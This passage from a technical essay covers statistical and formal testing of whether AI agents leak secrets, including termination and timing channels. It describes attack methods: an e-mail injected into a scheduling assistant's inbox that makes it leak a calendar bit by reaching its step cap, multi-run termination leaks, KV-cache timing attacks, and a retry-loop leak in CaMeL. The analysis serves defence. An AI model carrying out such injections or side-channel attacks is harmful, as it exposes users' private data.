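A tester who can read the model's token probabilities can make some comparisons without sampling. For example, the tester can read the probability of "10" under each calendar instead of running the assistant hundreds of times to estimate how often it offers slot 10.

The same idea works for longer texts. Let $C$ and $C'$ be what the model reads in two runs that differ only in the secret, and let $t_1, \ldots, t_n$ be the tokens of a fixed continuation $t$. The tester calculates how unlikely each token was, given those before it, and takes the average:

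$$\ell(C, t) = -\frac{1}{n}\sum_{i=1}^{n} \log p(t_i \mid C, t_1, \ldots, t_{i-1}), \qquad \Delta = \ell(C', t) - \ell(C, t).$$

If $\Delta$ is positive, the text is more likely with $C$ than with $C'$, by a factor of $\exp(n\Delta)$.

*Counterfactual Likelihood Tests for Indirect Influence in Private Reasoning Channels* used this method on the two-role system described earlier. The influence scores given there, 54.4% without a mask and 13.6% with one, are the shares of continuations for which $\Delta$ was positive. Planted strings missed this influence. Searching for shared phrases exaggerated it, giving 84% leakage in the masked version, mostly because both roles had independently derived the same equations.

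The average $\Delta$ was 0.068 without the mask and 0.022 with it. Small shifts per token compound, so over 100 tokens a shift of 0.068 makes a text about 900 times as likely, and 0.022 about nine times. A leak test should also count negative values, since a text that becomes more likely when the secret changes shows just as much dependence on it.

In the first version of the experiment, the replacement text often had a different length from the original, which shifted every later token and could alone change the scores. After the researcher matched the lengths, the first role's private text still influenced the second role in 25.3% of cases, compared with 2.0% in the opposite direction. The influence passed through the model's internal representation of the public words. When the researcher blocked that route in a larger experiment, the scores were identical in all 13,734 comparisons.

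A colleague who reads only the words of a message can't access these internal representations, but another agent that reuses them might be able to. The experiment used one family of 7-billion-parameter models and studied private reasoning, so its percentages don't measure how often agents leak their users' secrets.

In a leak test, the method covers only the texts that the tester scores, and another text might show a larger difference. It also measures the probability of a particular wording. The assistant might become more likely to write "How about 10?" and less likely to write "10 works" without changing how often it offers slot 10. Asking for the slot in a fixed format largely avoids this problem.

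Private reasoning also complicates the scoring. Suppose the assistant writes "the interview is at 9" in its private notes before making a proposal. That sentence is very unlikely with the other calendar, so scoring the notes would suggest a leak even if the proposal never depends on them. The tester should score only what the colleague sees, but the probability of a proposal is an average over all the notes that could have come before it, and estimating that average again requires sampling.

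The probabilities can also vary for the reasons already described. *Beyond Reproducibility* (2026) treats rounding as a shift in the token probabilities themselves, which matters at any temperature. A tester should therefore score each text more than once under the same secret to measure how much $\Delta$ varies by chance.

### How small differences grow

A changed token affects every token after it. In an agent, it can also change the next action, what the agent learns from that action, and everything it does afterwards. Hydari and Iqbal give the example of a database query that selects "active" customers in one run and "active" or "pending" customers in another. The queries are almost the same, but the agent receives different data and may then act quite differently.

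Nagisettygari and Sindiramutty's results show how quickly chance differences accumulate. In an experiment with maths problems, batching changed the chosen token at 197 of about 30,000 steps, or roughly 0.65%. Yet 53.8% of the answers differed, with an average length of only 119 tokens. This is about what we would expect if each token had an independent chance of changing:

$$1 - (1 - 0.0065)^{119} \approx 0.54.$$

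If an agent made ten model calls with the same chance of a difference, all ten would match only about 0.04% of the time. Many differences would be harmless changes in wording, but some could change what the agent does next.

A secret's influence can also grow with the number of messages. Suppose the assistant offers slot 10 in 55% of runs with a meeting and 50% with an interview. If a colleague receives ten independent proposals instead of one, the distance rises from 0.05 to about 0.13, and the colleague's best possible accuracy in guessing the secret rises from 52.5% to 56.4%. Testing a single message can therefore underestimate how much an agent leaks when it sends many.

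One way to stop harmless differences from accumulating is to compare one decision at a time. The tester records a run, gives the agent the same history with each secret in turn, and compares only the next action. If $h_i$ is the history before step $i$, then

$$\mathrm{TV}(P, Q) \;\le\; \sum_i \mathbb{E}\big[\,\mathrm{TV}\big(P(\cdot \mid h_i),\, Q(\cdot \mid h_i)\big)\big],$$

where the average is over histories from runs with the first secret. If the average distance is at most 0.01 at each of 20 steps, the distance for the whole run is at most 0.2.

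The recorded history has to make sense with both secrets. If the assistant has already mentioned the interview in its notes, those notes would almost never appear with the other calendar in normal use. The tester then has to compare whole runs and accept the extra variation.

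## How many runs are needed, and what does finding no difference show?

Suppose a tester runs the scheduling assistant many times on one task, with the same two calendars. As we saw, if either slot can appear with either calendar, no number of runs proves a leak. Runs can't rule out a leak either, because Pandey and colleagues show that, for any number of runs, some agent leaks so little that its results would look almost exactly like those of an agent that leaks nothing. The tester therefore has to decide how small a leak is worth finding and how often the test may be wrong.

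### Two coins

The number of runs needed grows with the inverse square of the size of the leak. *The Oversight Gap* proves this with a two-coin example. With the first calendar, the assistant offers slot 11 with probability 1/2. With the second, the probability is still 1/2 if there is no leak, but 1/2 + ε if there is one. The tester sees $k$ runs with each calendar and must decide whether there is a leak.

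1. One run with the second calendar says little. The Kullback–Leibler divergence, a standard measure of how strongly one observation favours one explanation over another, is about $2\varepsilon^2$.
2. The divergences of independent runs add up, so $k$ runs give about $2k\varepsilon^2$.
3. Pinsker's inequality limits the total variation distance to the square root of half the divergence, which is $\varepsilon\sqrt{k}$.
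4. By the same bound that applies to monitors, the tester's accuracy is at most $\tfrac12 + \tfrac12\,\varepsilon\sqrt{k}$.

Being right two times out of three therefore requires $k \ge 1/(9\varepsilon^2)$ runs per calendar. Detecting a leak of 5 percentage points takes about 44 runs per calendar, and halving the leak quadruples that number.

A simple test comes within a constant factor of this limit. For each calendar, the tester calculates the share of runs in which the assistant offered slot 11, then reports a leak if the two shares differ by more than ε/2. The random error in each share is proportional to $1/\sqrt{k}$, so it is small compared with ε once $k$ is a large enough multiple of $1/\varepsilon^2$.

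### The numbers for the scheduling assistant

Being right two times out of three is a low standard. A more usual one allows a 5% chance of a false alarm, counting differences in either direction, and demands an 80% chance of detecting the leak if it exists. If the assistant offers slot 10 with probability $p$ under one calendar and $q$ under the other, the number of runs per calendar is approximately

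$$n \approx \frac{(1.96 + 0.84)^2\,[\,p(1-p) + q(1-q)\,]}{(p-q)^2}.$$

The 1.96 comes from the 5% and the 0.84 from the 80%.

| Probability of slot 10 under the two calendars | Runs per calendar |
|---|---|
| 50% and 90% | 17 |
| 50% and 75% | 55 |
| 50% and 60% | 385 |
| 50% and 55% | 1,560 |
| 50% and 51% | 39,000 |
| 0% and 1% | 780 |

Tests with a few dozen runs can therefore find only large leaks. *The Envelope Layer* (2026), a study of defences for agents, reports that the smallest difference it could reliably detect was about 43 percentage points with 20 runs per condition and 19 points with 100. It treats its 20-run results as descriptive only.

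The last row of the table shows that the rates themselves matter, as well as the size of the difference between them. A difference of one percentage point is much easier to find near 0% than near 50%, because an assistant that almost never offers slot 10 produces little random variation to hide it.

Comparing how often each slot comes up also takes far fewer runs than counting the pairs of runs that differ. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* gives the example of an outcome with probability 0.5 in one condition and 0.6 in the other. Pairs with different secrets would differ only one percentage point more often than pairs in the same-secret baseline described earlier. Detecting that excess would take tens of thousands of pairs, while comparing the outcome's frequency in each condition can reveal the difference with 385 runs per condition.

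### Why two runs are sometimes enough

*The Oversight Gap* reports much better results with very few runs. In its customer-data test, each new run gave the other customer one of four values at random, and language models checked whether the assistant's answer changed. The table shows their average balanced accuracy.

| Method | 2 runs | 4 runs | 8 runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calculated for a perfect comparison | 87.5% | 99.2% | 100.0% |
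| Comparing only the stated value | 88.4% | 99.3% | 99.8% |
| Flagging any difference | 78.9% | 91.9% | 91.2% |

A leaking assistant always states the other customer's value, so the leak stays hidden only if every run draws the same value. This has probability $4^{1-k}$ for $k$ runs, or one in four for two runs and one in 64 for four. A perfect comparison never raises a false alarm, so its balanced accuracy is $1 - \tfrac12 \cdot 4^{1-k}$, which gives the first row of percentages.

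This is close to the deterministic case. The four values are distinct, the leak happens every time, and an assistant that doesn't leak always states the same value, however it words the sentence. A single change in the stated value is therefore enough to prove a leak. Repeating the runs helps only because it gives the other customer's value another chance to change.

If the leak were rarer but the clean answer just as stable, the tester would need more runs, though still far fewer than $1/\varepsilon^2$. An assistant that states the wrong value in 5% of runs has a 95% chance of doing so at least once in 59 runs. A good projection can greatly reduce the number of runs needed because it can remove the harmless variation that makes small leaks hard to detect.

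Few outcomes are this stable in practice. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* reran an attack benchmark through providers' services without changing anything, and the recorded outcome changed in 13.8% of cases for Gemini 3.8 Flash and 8.1% for Gemini 4 Argon.

### Many possible outputs

So far the assistant has had two slots to choose from. With more possible outputs, the tester also has to find where the difference lies. Statisticians call this problem closeness testing, in which the tester draws samples from two unknown distributions and must decide whether they are equal or at least a given distance apart.

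One approach counts how often each output $i$ appears under the two secrets, $X_i$ and $Y_i$, and adds up

$$(X_i - Y_i)^2 - X_i - Y_i$$

over all outputs. Subtracting the counts removes the part that chance would contribute, so the sum is close to zero on average if the distributions are equal and grows if they are not. A message that appears only once contributes 1 − 1 = 0. The test therefore learns only from messages that repeat, and with more possible messages, repeats take longer to appear.

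Chan, Valiant and colleagues (2013), in *Optimal Algorithms for Testing Closeness of Discrete Distributions*, established how many samples the best possible test needs. For $m$ possible outputs, the number is proportional to

$$\max\left\{\frac{m^{2/3}}{\varepsilon^{4/3}},\; \frac{m^{1/2}}{\varepsilon^{2}}\right\},$$

where ε is now the sum of the absolute differences in probability, or twice the total variation distance. For a small leak, going from 2 possible outputs to 200 multiplies the number of runs by about ten. The first term takes over when $m$ exceeds $1/\varepsilon^4$, which is 10,000 outputs for a distance of 0.05. The number of possible e-mails is vastly larger.

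Even a large leak can go undetected when there are many possible outputs. *Testing Closeness of Discrete Distributions* (2010) presents Valiant's theorem about pairs of distributions over $m$ outcomes with a total variation distance of 0.5. If the number of samples grows more slowly than $m^{2/3}$, any test will fail to distinguish some of these pairs from two identical distributions.

An assistant could pick about half of its replies from a short stock list that it uses with both calendars, and the rest from one of two enormous lists, one for each calendar. The tester would see the stock replies equally often with either calendar and hardly ever see any other reply twice. Yet a colleague who knew the two enormous lists could identify the calendar from a single reply about half the time.

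These worst cases assume that the outputs have no structure the tester can use. Real messages have structure, and projecting them onto the offered slot reduces $m$ to the number of free slots.

### Training a classifier to find the difference

A tester who doesn't know which feature of the messages might carry the secret can train a classifier to look for it. *Revisiting Classifier Two-Sample Tests* (2016) develops this idea. The tester labels each message with the secret behind it, trains the classifier on some of the messages, and measures its accuracy on the rest. If the secret makes no difference to the messages, the classifier should be right about half the time.

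If the tester holds back 200 messages, 100 for each secret, a classifier that is only guessing will get 113 or more right about 4% of the time. A score of at least 113 (56.5%) is therefore evidence of a leak, provided the tester randomised the order of the runs. The accuracy also gives a minimum size for the leak. No classifier's true accuracy can exceed one half plus half the total variation distance, so a true accuracy of 60% implies a distance of at least 0.2.

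A low score is harder to interpret. If the assistant offers slot 10 in 55% of runs with one calendar and 50% with the other, even the best possible classifier that sees only the slot is right 52.5% of the time, so this test would usually miss the leak. The classifier may also fail to learn a pattern that someone else knows, as happened to the reader model with the stock jokes. *Two-sample test based on Self-Organizing Maps* (2022) adds that the method is poorly suited to small samples, because the messages used for training can't count towards the result.

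### Stopping early and testing many things

If a tester applies an ordinary 5% test after each batch and stops as soon as a difference is significant, the false-alarm rate rises above 5%, to about 19% for ten equal batches.

Some tests stay valid no matter how often the tester checks the results. For example, the tester can do the runs in pairs, one with each calendar, and keep a score that starts at 1. If both runs offer the same slot, the score stays the same. If only the interview run offers slot 11, the tester multiplies the score by 1.5, and if only the meeting run does, by 0.5. When the calendar has no effect, these last two cases are equally likely, so the score neither rises nor falls on average. A theorem about fair games then implies that the score has at most a 5% chance of ever reaching 20.

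The assistant that always signals the interview reaches 20 after eight pairs, and the tester can stop there. Detecting small leaks requires multipliers closer to 1. With multipliers of 1.1 and 0.9, an assistant that offers slot 11 in 50% of interview runs and 45% of meeting runs takes roughly 1,200 pairs on average to reach 20.

Testing more features also raises the number of false alarms. A tester who checks 20 features of the messages at the 5% level has a 64% chance of at least one false alarm if the features are independent and none depends on the secret. The simplest correction is to divide the 5% by 20 and test each feature at the 0.25% level. *The Envelope Layer* uses the less strict Benjamini–Hochberg correction, which limits the expected share of false alarms among the differences reported.

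The correction requires fewer extra runs than one might expect. At 0.25%, telling 50% from 55% takes about 2,970 runs per calendar instead of 1,560. *Optimal Testing of Discrete Distributions with High Probability* (2020) shows that the increase is also modest when there are many possible outputs. The number of runs then grows at most in proportion to the logarithm of $1/\delta$, where δ is the permitted error probability. Very small tests are an exception, because the permutation test with five runs per calendar can't produce a probability below 1 in 252, or about 0.4%, and so can't meet the 0.25% threshold.

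Combining results can reveal a small effect more reliably than testing each one separately. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* simulated a defence that lowered the success rate of attacks by three percentage points across 400 test cases. Comparing the average success rate over six runs with the defence and six without it detected the effect in all 2,000 simulations, while comparing single runs detected it in only 29.5%. A tester could average over many scheduling tasks in the same way, but only if the secret shifts the assistant's behaviour in the same direction in most of them.

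### Reporting that nothing was found

A test that finds no difference may have been too small to detect one. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* describes a defence that repeats the user's task after every tool result. The defence lowered one agent's attack success rate by 4.5 percentage points in one comparison and 1.8 in another, but neither drop was large enough to be attributed to the defence under the study's strictest test. A later comparison of eight fresh runs with the defence and eight without it confirmed a drop of 4.8 points.

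A null result should therefore include an upper limit on what the test could have missed. Pandey and colleagues do this for their audit of Claude Sonnet 4.6, which found no failures in 80 episodes. If each episode fails independently with probability $r$, the probability of no failures is $(1-r)^{80}$. Setting this to 5% gives

$$r = 1 - 0.05^{1/80} \approx 3.7\%.$$

If the true failure rate were above 3.7%, the audit would have had less than a 5% chance of finding no failures. As a rule of thumb, this upper limit is three divided by the number of runs. Lowering it to 1% takes about 300 runs without a failure, and lowering it to 0.1% takes about 3,000. The audit's ten-episode tests of planted instructions and consent also found no failures, but their limit is 26%.

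The 3.7% is a limit on the failure rate per episode, whereas noninterference compares two distributions. To translate between them, suppose that half the episodes used each hidden reason and that a failure means any departure from the assistant's usual offer. Failures might occur with only one of the reasons, which the tester tried 40 times. The limit on the total variation distance is then $1 - 0.05^{1/40}$, or 7.2%, so a colleague could guess the reason from one proposal with at most 53.6% accuracy.

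This calculation works only because the assistant's usual offer is stable. Suppose the assistant instead chose between slots 10 and 11 at random, and offered each slot 20 times with each reason. The tester would also find no difference, but the 95% confidence interval for the difference would run from about −22 to +22 percentage points.

When a policy permits a small leak, as *PACE* does with its margin δ, the tester should choose the margin first and pass the agent only if the whole interval lies within it. With a margin of 5 points, the coin-tossing assistant needs about 2,100 runs per calendar to have an 80% chance of passing, even if it leaks nothing.

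The limit from the audit applies only to the task, hidden reasons, model and settings that Pandey and colleagues used, and to the parts of the message that their projection kept. It does not cover other secrets or a newer version of the model. It also assumes that the episodes were independent, so 80 episodes that shared a cached answer would be much weaker evidence. At a rate of 3.7%, an assistant that handles a thousand requests could still fail dozens of times.

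A useful report might read: "In 40 runs with each of these two calendars, the assistant always offered the same slots. With 95% confidence, the distance between the two distributions of offers is below 7.2%. We did not compare wording or timing."

### Measuring a leak in bits

Instead of a yes-or-no verdict, a tester can estimate how much the output helps an observer guess the secret. Min-entropy leakage measures this in bits. Let $V_0$ be the observer's best chance of guessing the secret in one try before seeing the output, and $V_1$ the average chance afterwards. The leakage is

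$$L = \log_2 \frac{V_1}{V_0}.$$

A leak of one bit means that the output doubles the observer's chance of guessing the secret. Suppose a meeting and an interview are equally likely, and the assistant offers slot 10 in 55% of runs with the meeting and 50% with the interview. The colleague's chance of guessing correctly rises from 50% to 52.5%, so the leakage is $\log_2 1.05$, or about 0.07 bits. The assistant that always signals the interview leaks the whole secret, which is 1 bit.

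An older measure, mutual information, gives the average reduction in uncertainty about the secret. Smith (2011), in *Quantifying information flow using min-entropy*, argues that it doesn't provide satisfactory security guarantees. For example, one agent might reveal a random 64-bit key in an eighth of its runs and nothing in the rest, while another always reveals the key's first eight bits. Mutual information is 8 bits for both. But an observer of the first agent can name the key about one time in eight, while an observer of the second has almost no chance. Min-entropy leakage is about 61 bits for the first agent and 8 bits for the second.

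*LeakWatch* (Chothia, Kawamoto and Novakovic, 2014) describes a tool that estimates both measures for Java programs. The tester marks the secret and the visible values in the code, and the tool runs the program repeatedly and counts how often each combination occurs. It also calculates a confidence interval and checks whether the apparent leak is consistent with zero.

In one example, four diners use a protocol that reveals whether one of them paid the bill but not who. The content of the messages doesn't identify the payer, but the order of the announcements provides a clue, because the payer has to send payment details first and so tends to announce a result late. After 6,080 runs, LeakWatch estimated a leak of 0.47 bits, which raises an observer's chance of naming the payer from 25% to about 35%. Adding a delay before each announcement made the order less predictable, and the tool found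 no remaining leak after 5,700 runs.

Counting works only if the outputs repeat. Suppose an assistant ignores the secret but never writes the same message twice. Each message then appears with only one of the calendars, so the estimated leak is 1 bit, as if the message identified the calendar perfectly. LeakWatch guards against this by continuing until new outputs stop appearing and there are at least four times as many runs as combinations of secret and output, though it might never stop if the outputs are free text.

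*F-BLEAU* (Cherubin, Chatzikokolakis and Palamidessi, 2019) trains a classifier to guess the secret and uses its error rate to estimate the leakage. A classifier based on counts cannot use an output it has not seen before to guess the secret, so with too few runs it tends to understate the leak. A nearest-neighbour classifier instead guesses the secret behind the most similar output it has seen. On an artificial system with 100 secrets and 10,000 outputs, the nearest-neighbour classifier needed 333 examples for an accurate estimate, while the count-based one needed 35,016.

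The nearest-neighbour method's advantage over counting depends on similar outputs coming from the same secret. When the outputs were noisier, the two methods needed almost the same number of examples, about 153,000. On a system built so that neighbouring outputs came from different secrets, the nearest-neighbour method needed more examples than counting did. Cherubin and colleagues point out that no estimator can guarantee its accuracy on a finite sample for every system, and they recommend trying several.

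To use this method on an agent's messages, a tester would have to choose how to measure similarity between texts. A measure based on meaning might group together the many ways of offering slot 10, but it would probably miss a secret that affects only the punctuation.

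## What does cutting runs off after a fixed number of steps leave out?

An agent may never finish, so a tester has to stop each run after a fixed number of steps, say 40. Suppose the scheduling assistant proposes slot 10 at step 12 when the hidden reason is an ordinary meeting, but is still working at step 40 when the reason is an interview. Only one run contains a proposal, so the tester has to decide whether the pair counts as a leak. People who verify ordinary programs face the same question about infinite loops, and most of their tools don't address it.

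### Ignoring runs that do not finish

Termination-insensitive noninterference, as mentioned earlier, applies only to pairs of runs that both finish. The following program satisfies it:

```
if secret == 0: loop forever
send("done")
```

Every finished run sends the same message. But someone who waits in vain for the message can conclude that the secret is 0.

Verifiers leave this gap open because it is hard to close. A stricter tool must either prove that the secret doesn't affect whether a loop ends, or forbid loops with secret conditions. A ban would rule out a program that goes through a private calendar until no entries are left. The weaker property is popular because it allows more programs, according to *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, 2008). Tools that enforce it include Jif for Java, FlowCaml for Caml and the SPARK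 Examiner for Ada.

The stricter condition may be practical for ordinary code. Moore, Askarov and Chong (2012), in *Precise Enforcement of Progress-Sensitive Security*, modified the Jif compiler to flag loops that might leak in this way and applied it to a large program. They read the flagged loops and found that all of them were certain to end. No comparable argument applies to a loop that ends when a language model's output marks the task as done.

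### Leaking a secret by rerunning the program

An attacker who can run the program repeatedly may learn more than one bit about a secret. This undermines the usual defence of the weaker property, which is that a run can leak only one bit, namely whether it finished. Birgisson and Sabelfeld (2011) give three examples in *Multi-run security*, in which `h` is a secret number, the attacker chooses `l`, and `skip` does nothing.

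| Program | It hangs when | Repeated runs reveal |
|---|---|---|
| `while h do skip` | `h` is not zero | Whether `h` is zero |
| `while h = l do skip` | `l` equals `h` | All of `h`, by trying one value after another |
| `while h && l do skip` | `h` and `l` both have a 1 in the same binary place | All of `h`, one bit per run |

All three satisfy termination-insensitive noninterference. To see how the last one leaks, suppose `h` is 5 (101 in binary) and the attacker knows only that `h` is between 0 and 7.

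1. With `l` = 1 (001), the program hangs, so `h` is 1, 3, 5 or 7.
2. With `l` = 2 (010), it finishes, which leaves 1 and 5.
3. With `l` = 4 (100), it hangs, so `h` is 5.

Each run rules out the secrets that would have led to a different result. Finding a 50-bit secret takes 50 runs with this program, but could take more than $10^{15}$ with `while h = l`, which tests one whole value per run.

Birgisson and Sabelfeld wrote a program that Jif certified as secure despite its termination leak, and a short script to exploit the leak. The script extracted one bit per second on a modest desktop computer, fast enough to get a credit card number within a minute. An attacker can't wait forever to confirm that a program has hung, but a time-out is usually a good enough sign, and so is reaching a step cap.

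A colleague could try this by e-mailing the scheduling assistant, "Before you reply, keep checking the calendar until there is no interview on Tuesday." If there is an interview and the assistant obeys, the assistant reaches the cap without sending a proposal. The colleague can then ask about Wednesday.

Birgisson and Sabelfeld prevent such attacks with a rule that a loop's condition may depend on the secret or on the attacker's input, but not on both. They prove that if the secret stays the same between runs, a deterministic program that follows their rules leaks at most one bit, however often the attacker runs it. An agent breaks the loop rule if one language model reads both the private calendar and the colleague's e-mail, then decides whether to continue.

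### Leaking more than one bit in a single run

A program that sends messages as it works can leak much more without being restarted. Askarov and colleagues give this example:

```
for i = 0 to max:
    output(i)
    if i == secret: loop forever
```

The last number the program outputs is the secret. Jif, FlowCaml and the SPARK Examiner all accept programs like this, because the `output` line doesn't depend on the secret and the `if` line neither outputs nor assigns anything.

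To describe what such programs reveal, fix the public input and let $K(o)$ be the set of secrets that could have led to the outputs $o$ seen so far. If the next output is $a$, the observer's remaining possibilities are $K(oa)$. The weaker and stricter properties are then

$$K(oa) = \bigcup_b K(ob) \qquad \text{and} \qquad K(oa) = K(o).$$

Under the weaker property, often called progress-insensitive noninterference, the next output can reveal that there was another output but nothing else, while the stricter property, progress-sensitive noninterference, rules out even that. The counting program satisfies the weaker property because the next number is always predictable, but it fails the stricter one because each new number rules out one more secret.

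In an experiment on a 3 GHz computer, this method leaked a 32-bit secret in under six seconds. Askarov and colleagues estimate that leaking a 50-bit credit card number would take about 18.5 days, and that leaking a 128-bit key would be infeasible. The rerunning attack extracts a card number much faster because each run can halve the remaining possibilities, while each output in this method rules out only one.

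They also prove that a program with the weaker property can't do much better than count. For a given public input, its outputs always follow one fixed sequence, and the secret affects only where the sequence stops. An observer who watches for at most $t$ outputs can therefore make at most $t + 1$ different observations. Learning an $N$-bit secret with certainty takes at least $2^N - 1$ outputs. If all values are equally likely, the chance of guessing the secret after $t$ outputs is at most

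$$\frac{t + 1}{2^N}.$$

For a random 128-bit key, this chance stays below $10^{-29}$ even with a billion outputs. Large random secrets therefore remain safe in a single run, but the result does not protect a calendar if the secret is whether it contains an interview, because that is only one bit.

Crashes can leak secrets in the same way. Askarov and colleagues replaced the endless loop with a stack overflow, and the program still leaked its secret. A tester should look at runs that end in an error as well as those that reach the step limit.

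Running several processes at once can also turn many small leaks into a large one. Birgisson and Sabelfeld describe a program with one thread for each bit of the secret. Each thread hangs if its bit is 1 and otherwise outputs its own number, so the missing numbers reveal the whole secret in one run. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld (2014) show more generally in *Compositional Information-flow Security for Interactive Systems* that two systems with the weaker property can be insecure when combined, while systems with the stricter property stay secure. If the scheduling assistant gives each weekday to a separate helper agent, a colleague might see which helpers reply, so the tester should test all the agents together.

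### What to do with a run that reaches the cap

A tester can discard every pair that contains a capped run, record "cap reached" as the run's result, or compare what the observer has seen so far at each step. The table shows the result of each choice for three pairs of runs of a deterministic assistant.

| Pair of runs | Discard the pair | Record "cap reached" | Compare every step |
|---|---|---|---|
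| One run offers slot 10 and finishes, the other reaches the cap without an offer | Ignored | Leak | Leak |
| The runs offer different slots, then both reach the cap | Ignored | No difference | Leak |
| Both runs offer slot 10, one at step 12 and one at step 30, then reach the cap | Ignored | No difference | Leak |

For programs that produce one result at the end, discarding pairs amounts to testing termination-insensitive noninterference. But it is a poor choice for agents that send messages along the way. In the second row, for example, the two offers already prove a leak.

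For a random agent, discarding runs also distorts the comparison of those that remain. Suppose the assistant behaves as follows:

| Hidden reason | Offers slot 10 | Offers slot 11 | Never finishes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Meeting | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| Interview | 25% | 50% | 25% |

The assistant tosses a fair coin to choose between slots 10 and 11 whether or not there is an interview, but when there is one, it gets stuck in half of the runs in which it would have offered slot 10. Slot 11 then makes up two thirds of the offers in the finished interview runs, so a tester who discards unfinished runs measures a distance of about 0.17. The real distance is 0.25 if the colleague can tell that no offer came. Discarding would hide the leak completely if the assistant got stuck in a quarter of interview runs regardless of the coin, because the finished runs would have the same split of offers with and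 without an interview.

In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) tried to define the weaker property for random programs by comparing only finished runs, but concluded that this was wrong. They instead call two distributions compatible if adding results for the unfinished runs could make the distributions equal. The distributions in the table are compatible because the missing 25% could all have been offers of slot 10.

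Recording "cap reached" is better when the observer can tell that the agent gave up. The tester should keep any messages sent before the cap as well, which would also catch the leak in the second row. If the calendar's owner accepts that a missing reply may reveal something, the policy should list this as a permitted release. *Reconciling progress-insensitive noninterference and declassification* (Bay and Askarov, 2020) takes this approach in a programming language. The programmer must mark each block of code whose completion may reveal a secret, and the rest of the program must meet the stricter condition.

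Bay and Askarov describe a consensus that the weaker property suits trusted code, where the aim is to prevent accidents, but not untrusted code. An agent that reads e-mails from strangers is closer to untrusted code, because one of those e-mails may contain instructions for when the agent should stop.

Comparing every step tests the stricter property and catches all three differences, but the third matters only if the observer can see when a message was sent. The number of steps also varies by chance. One agent called its tools in the same order across three identical runs in only 26% of cases. A tester who includes step numbers therefore has to compare the distributions of those numbers.

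For most agents, I would compare the visible messages in order, with "cap reached" as a final message, and add step numbers only if the observer can see them.

The test should also use the same step limit as the real assistant. If the real assistant may take 100 steps, a run that the tester stopped at step 40 might have sent its offer at step 41. Before reporting a missing offer as a leak, the tester should let the run continue.

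### How much the stopping step can reveal

An observer who sees at which of 40 steps the agent stopped can make 40 different observations. One run can therefore reveal at most

$$\log_2 40 \approx 5.3 \text{ bits}.$$

An agent reaches this limit if there are 40 equally likely secrets and it stops at a different step for each. The observer's chance of guessing the secret then rises from 1 in 40 to certainty. If the observer sees only whether the agent replied, the limit is 1 bit.

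Ten runs together could reveal up to 53 bits, enough for a 50-bit card number if the agent encodes a different part of it in each run. Random variation in the number of steps would normally make the leak much smaller.

Moore and colleagues use this kind of calculation to limit leaks. Their system counts the public outputs that might reveal whether a secret-dependent loop has ended, and stops the program before the count exceeds a limit $B$. An observer can then learn at most $\log_2(B + 1)$ bits from the program's progress. For the same reason, an agent's operator could limit how many requests each person may send.

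### Leaks that begin after the cap

Two runs that agree for 40 steps may differ at step 41. If the agent has memory, a difference may not appear until a later session, even if every session finishes well before the step limit.

Bay and Askarov describe a news widget that keeps a private counter between uses and contacts its server whenever the counter is a multiple of ten. If the counter starts at 1 in one run and 2 in the other, neither widget contacts the server during the first eight uses. Only the second does on the ninth, so a tester who stopped after eight uses would miss the difference.

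The scheduling assistant might read about the interview on Monday and save the note "prefers late slots this week". Its Monday proposal could be the same with either calendar, while the note changes its Tuesday proposal. To catch this, the tester has to keep the memory from each Monday run, start a Tuesday session with each saved memory, and make the same request in both sessions.

Birgisson and Sabelfeld point out that running a program repeatedly is equivalent to running one longer program that loops. Their loop restores the secret before each repetition. For an agent with memory, the loop should also carry over whatever the agent saved, and the cap then limits the number of sessions as well as the steps in each.

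No fixed number of sessions is enough to check every agent, because an agent could always leak the secret in the session after the last one checked. Comparing the memory saved after the first session can help. If a deterministic agent saves exactly the same memory with either secret, that session can't cause a difference later, although later sessions may still leak the secret if they read it again. Different memories are a warning but don't prove a leak, because the agent may be allowed to store private information for its user.

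### Timing

Two runs can contain the same steps and still take different amounts of time. If the assistant thinks for longer when it finds an interview, the colleague may notice that the proposal arrives later.

Outsiders can use timing as well. *Whisper Leak* (2025) analyses the sizes and timing of network packets during a streamed answer. It also describes an earlier attack that uses the total response time to estimate how many tokens a model produced. A log that lists only messages and tool calls contains neither the packet data nor the response time.

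Some timing attacks closely resemble `while h = l`. They exploit servers that save work from one prompt and reuse it for another that begins the same way. *Selective KV-Cache Sharing to Mitigate Timing Side-Channels in LLM Inference* (2025) explains how an attacker can send guesses about another user's prompt and measure how quickly each answer starts. A fast start suggests that the guess matches saved work, and by repeating this the attacker can reconstruct parts of the prompt.

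*Mirage* (2026) describes a defence that, after detecting enough suspicious guesses, makes the timing of the whole answer look as if the server had reused nothing. It still leaks some information during the first few guesses. It also doesn't hide the number of tokens, so it would not conceal that the assistant had thought for longer about an interview.

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) recommends making sensitive operations always take their worst-case time. For an agent, the worst case is a run that reaches the step cap, so every reply would take as long as the slowest such run. Secure multi-execution can close termination and timing channels by using a separate copy of the program to produce public outputs. That copy never receives the secret and never waits for the copy that does.

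### The retry loop in CaMeL

Agents often retry after a failure, which can turn a one-bit leak into a much larger one within a single task. Garby and colleagues found such a leak in CaMeL, the system described earlier that has a language model write a program and tracks data while the program runs.

CaMeL's interpreter checks the security policy, but an ordinary Python loop outside the interpreter restarts the program after a failure. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, and the loop doesn't track that dependence. A program can therefore test one bit of the secret in each attempt and use the result to choose the next test, as Birgisson and Sabelfeld's attacker does. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes to the next attempt, but according to Garby and colleagues, this has no formal guarantee.

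A paired test should count the whole retry loop as one run. If the tester compared only single attempts and discarded the blocked ones, the results would not show the leak.

Garby and colleagues avoid retries on real data. Their agent, Randori, first tests its program on invented data, where the payment tool does nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. It revises the program until it works there, then writes a final version to run once on the real data. The agent can't catch a policy error in the real run and continue, because whether the error occurs may depend on a secret. Running only once on real data also avoids repeating a payment after a failed attempt.

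### A proof for agent programs

Randori is written in LLMbda, the agent programming language mentioned earlier. Its main theorem is the proof-based counterpart to a paired test. For any LLMbda program, if two inputs differ only in their secrets, the two distributions of visible results are compatible in the sense described above. This holds even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted inputs.

The proof uses an imaginary version of the program that skips each computation as soon as its label becomes secret. This version behaves identically with either secret and produces each visible result at least as often as the real program does. Its distribution therefore covers the real program's distributions for both secrets, as compatibility requires. Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean, a proof assistant.

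The theorem has several conditions:

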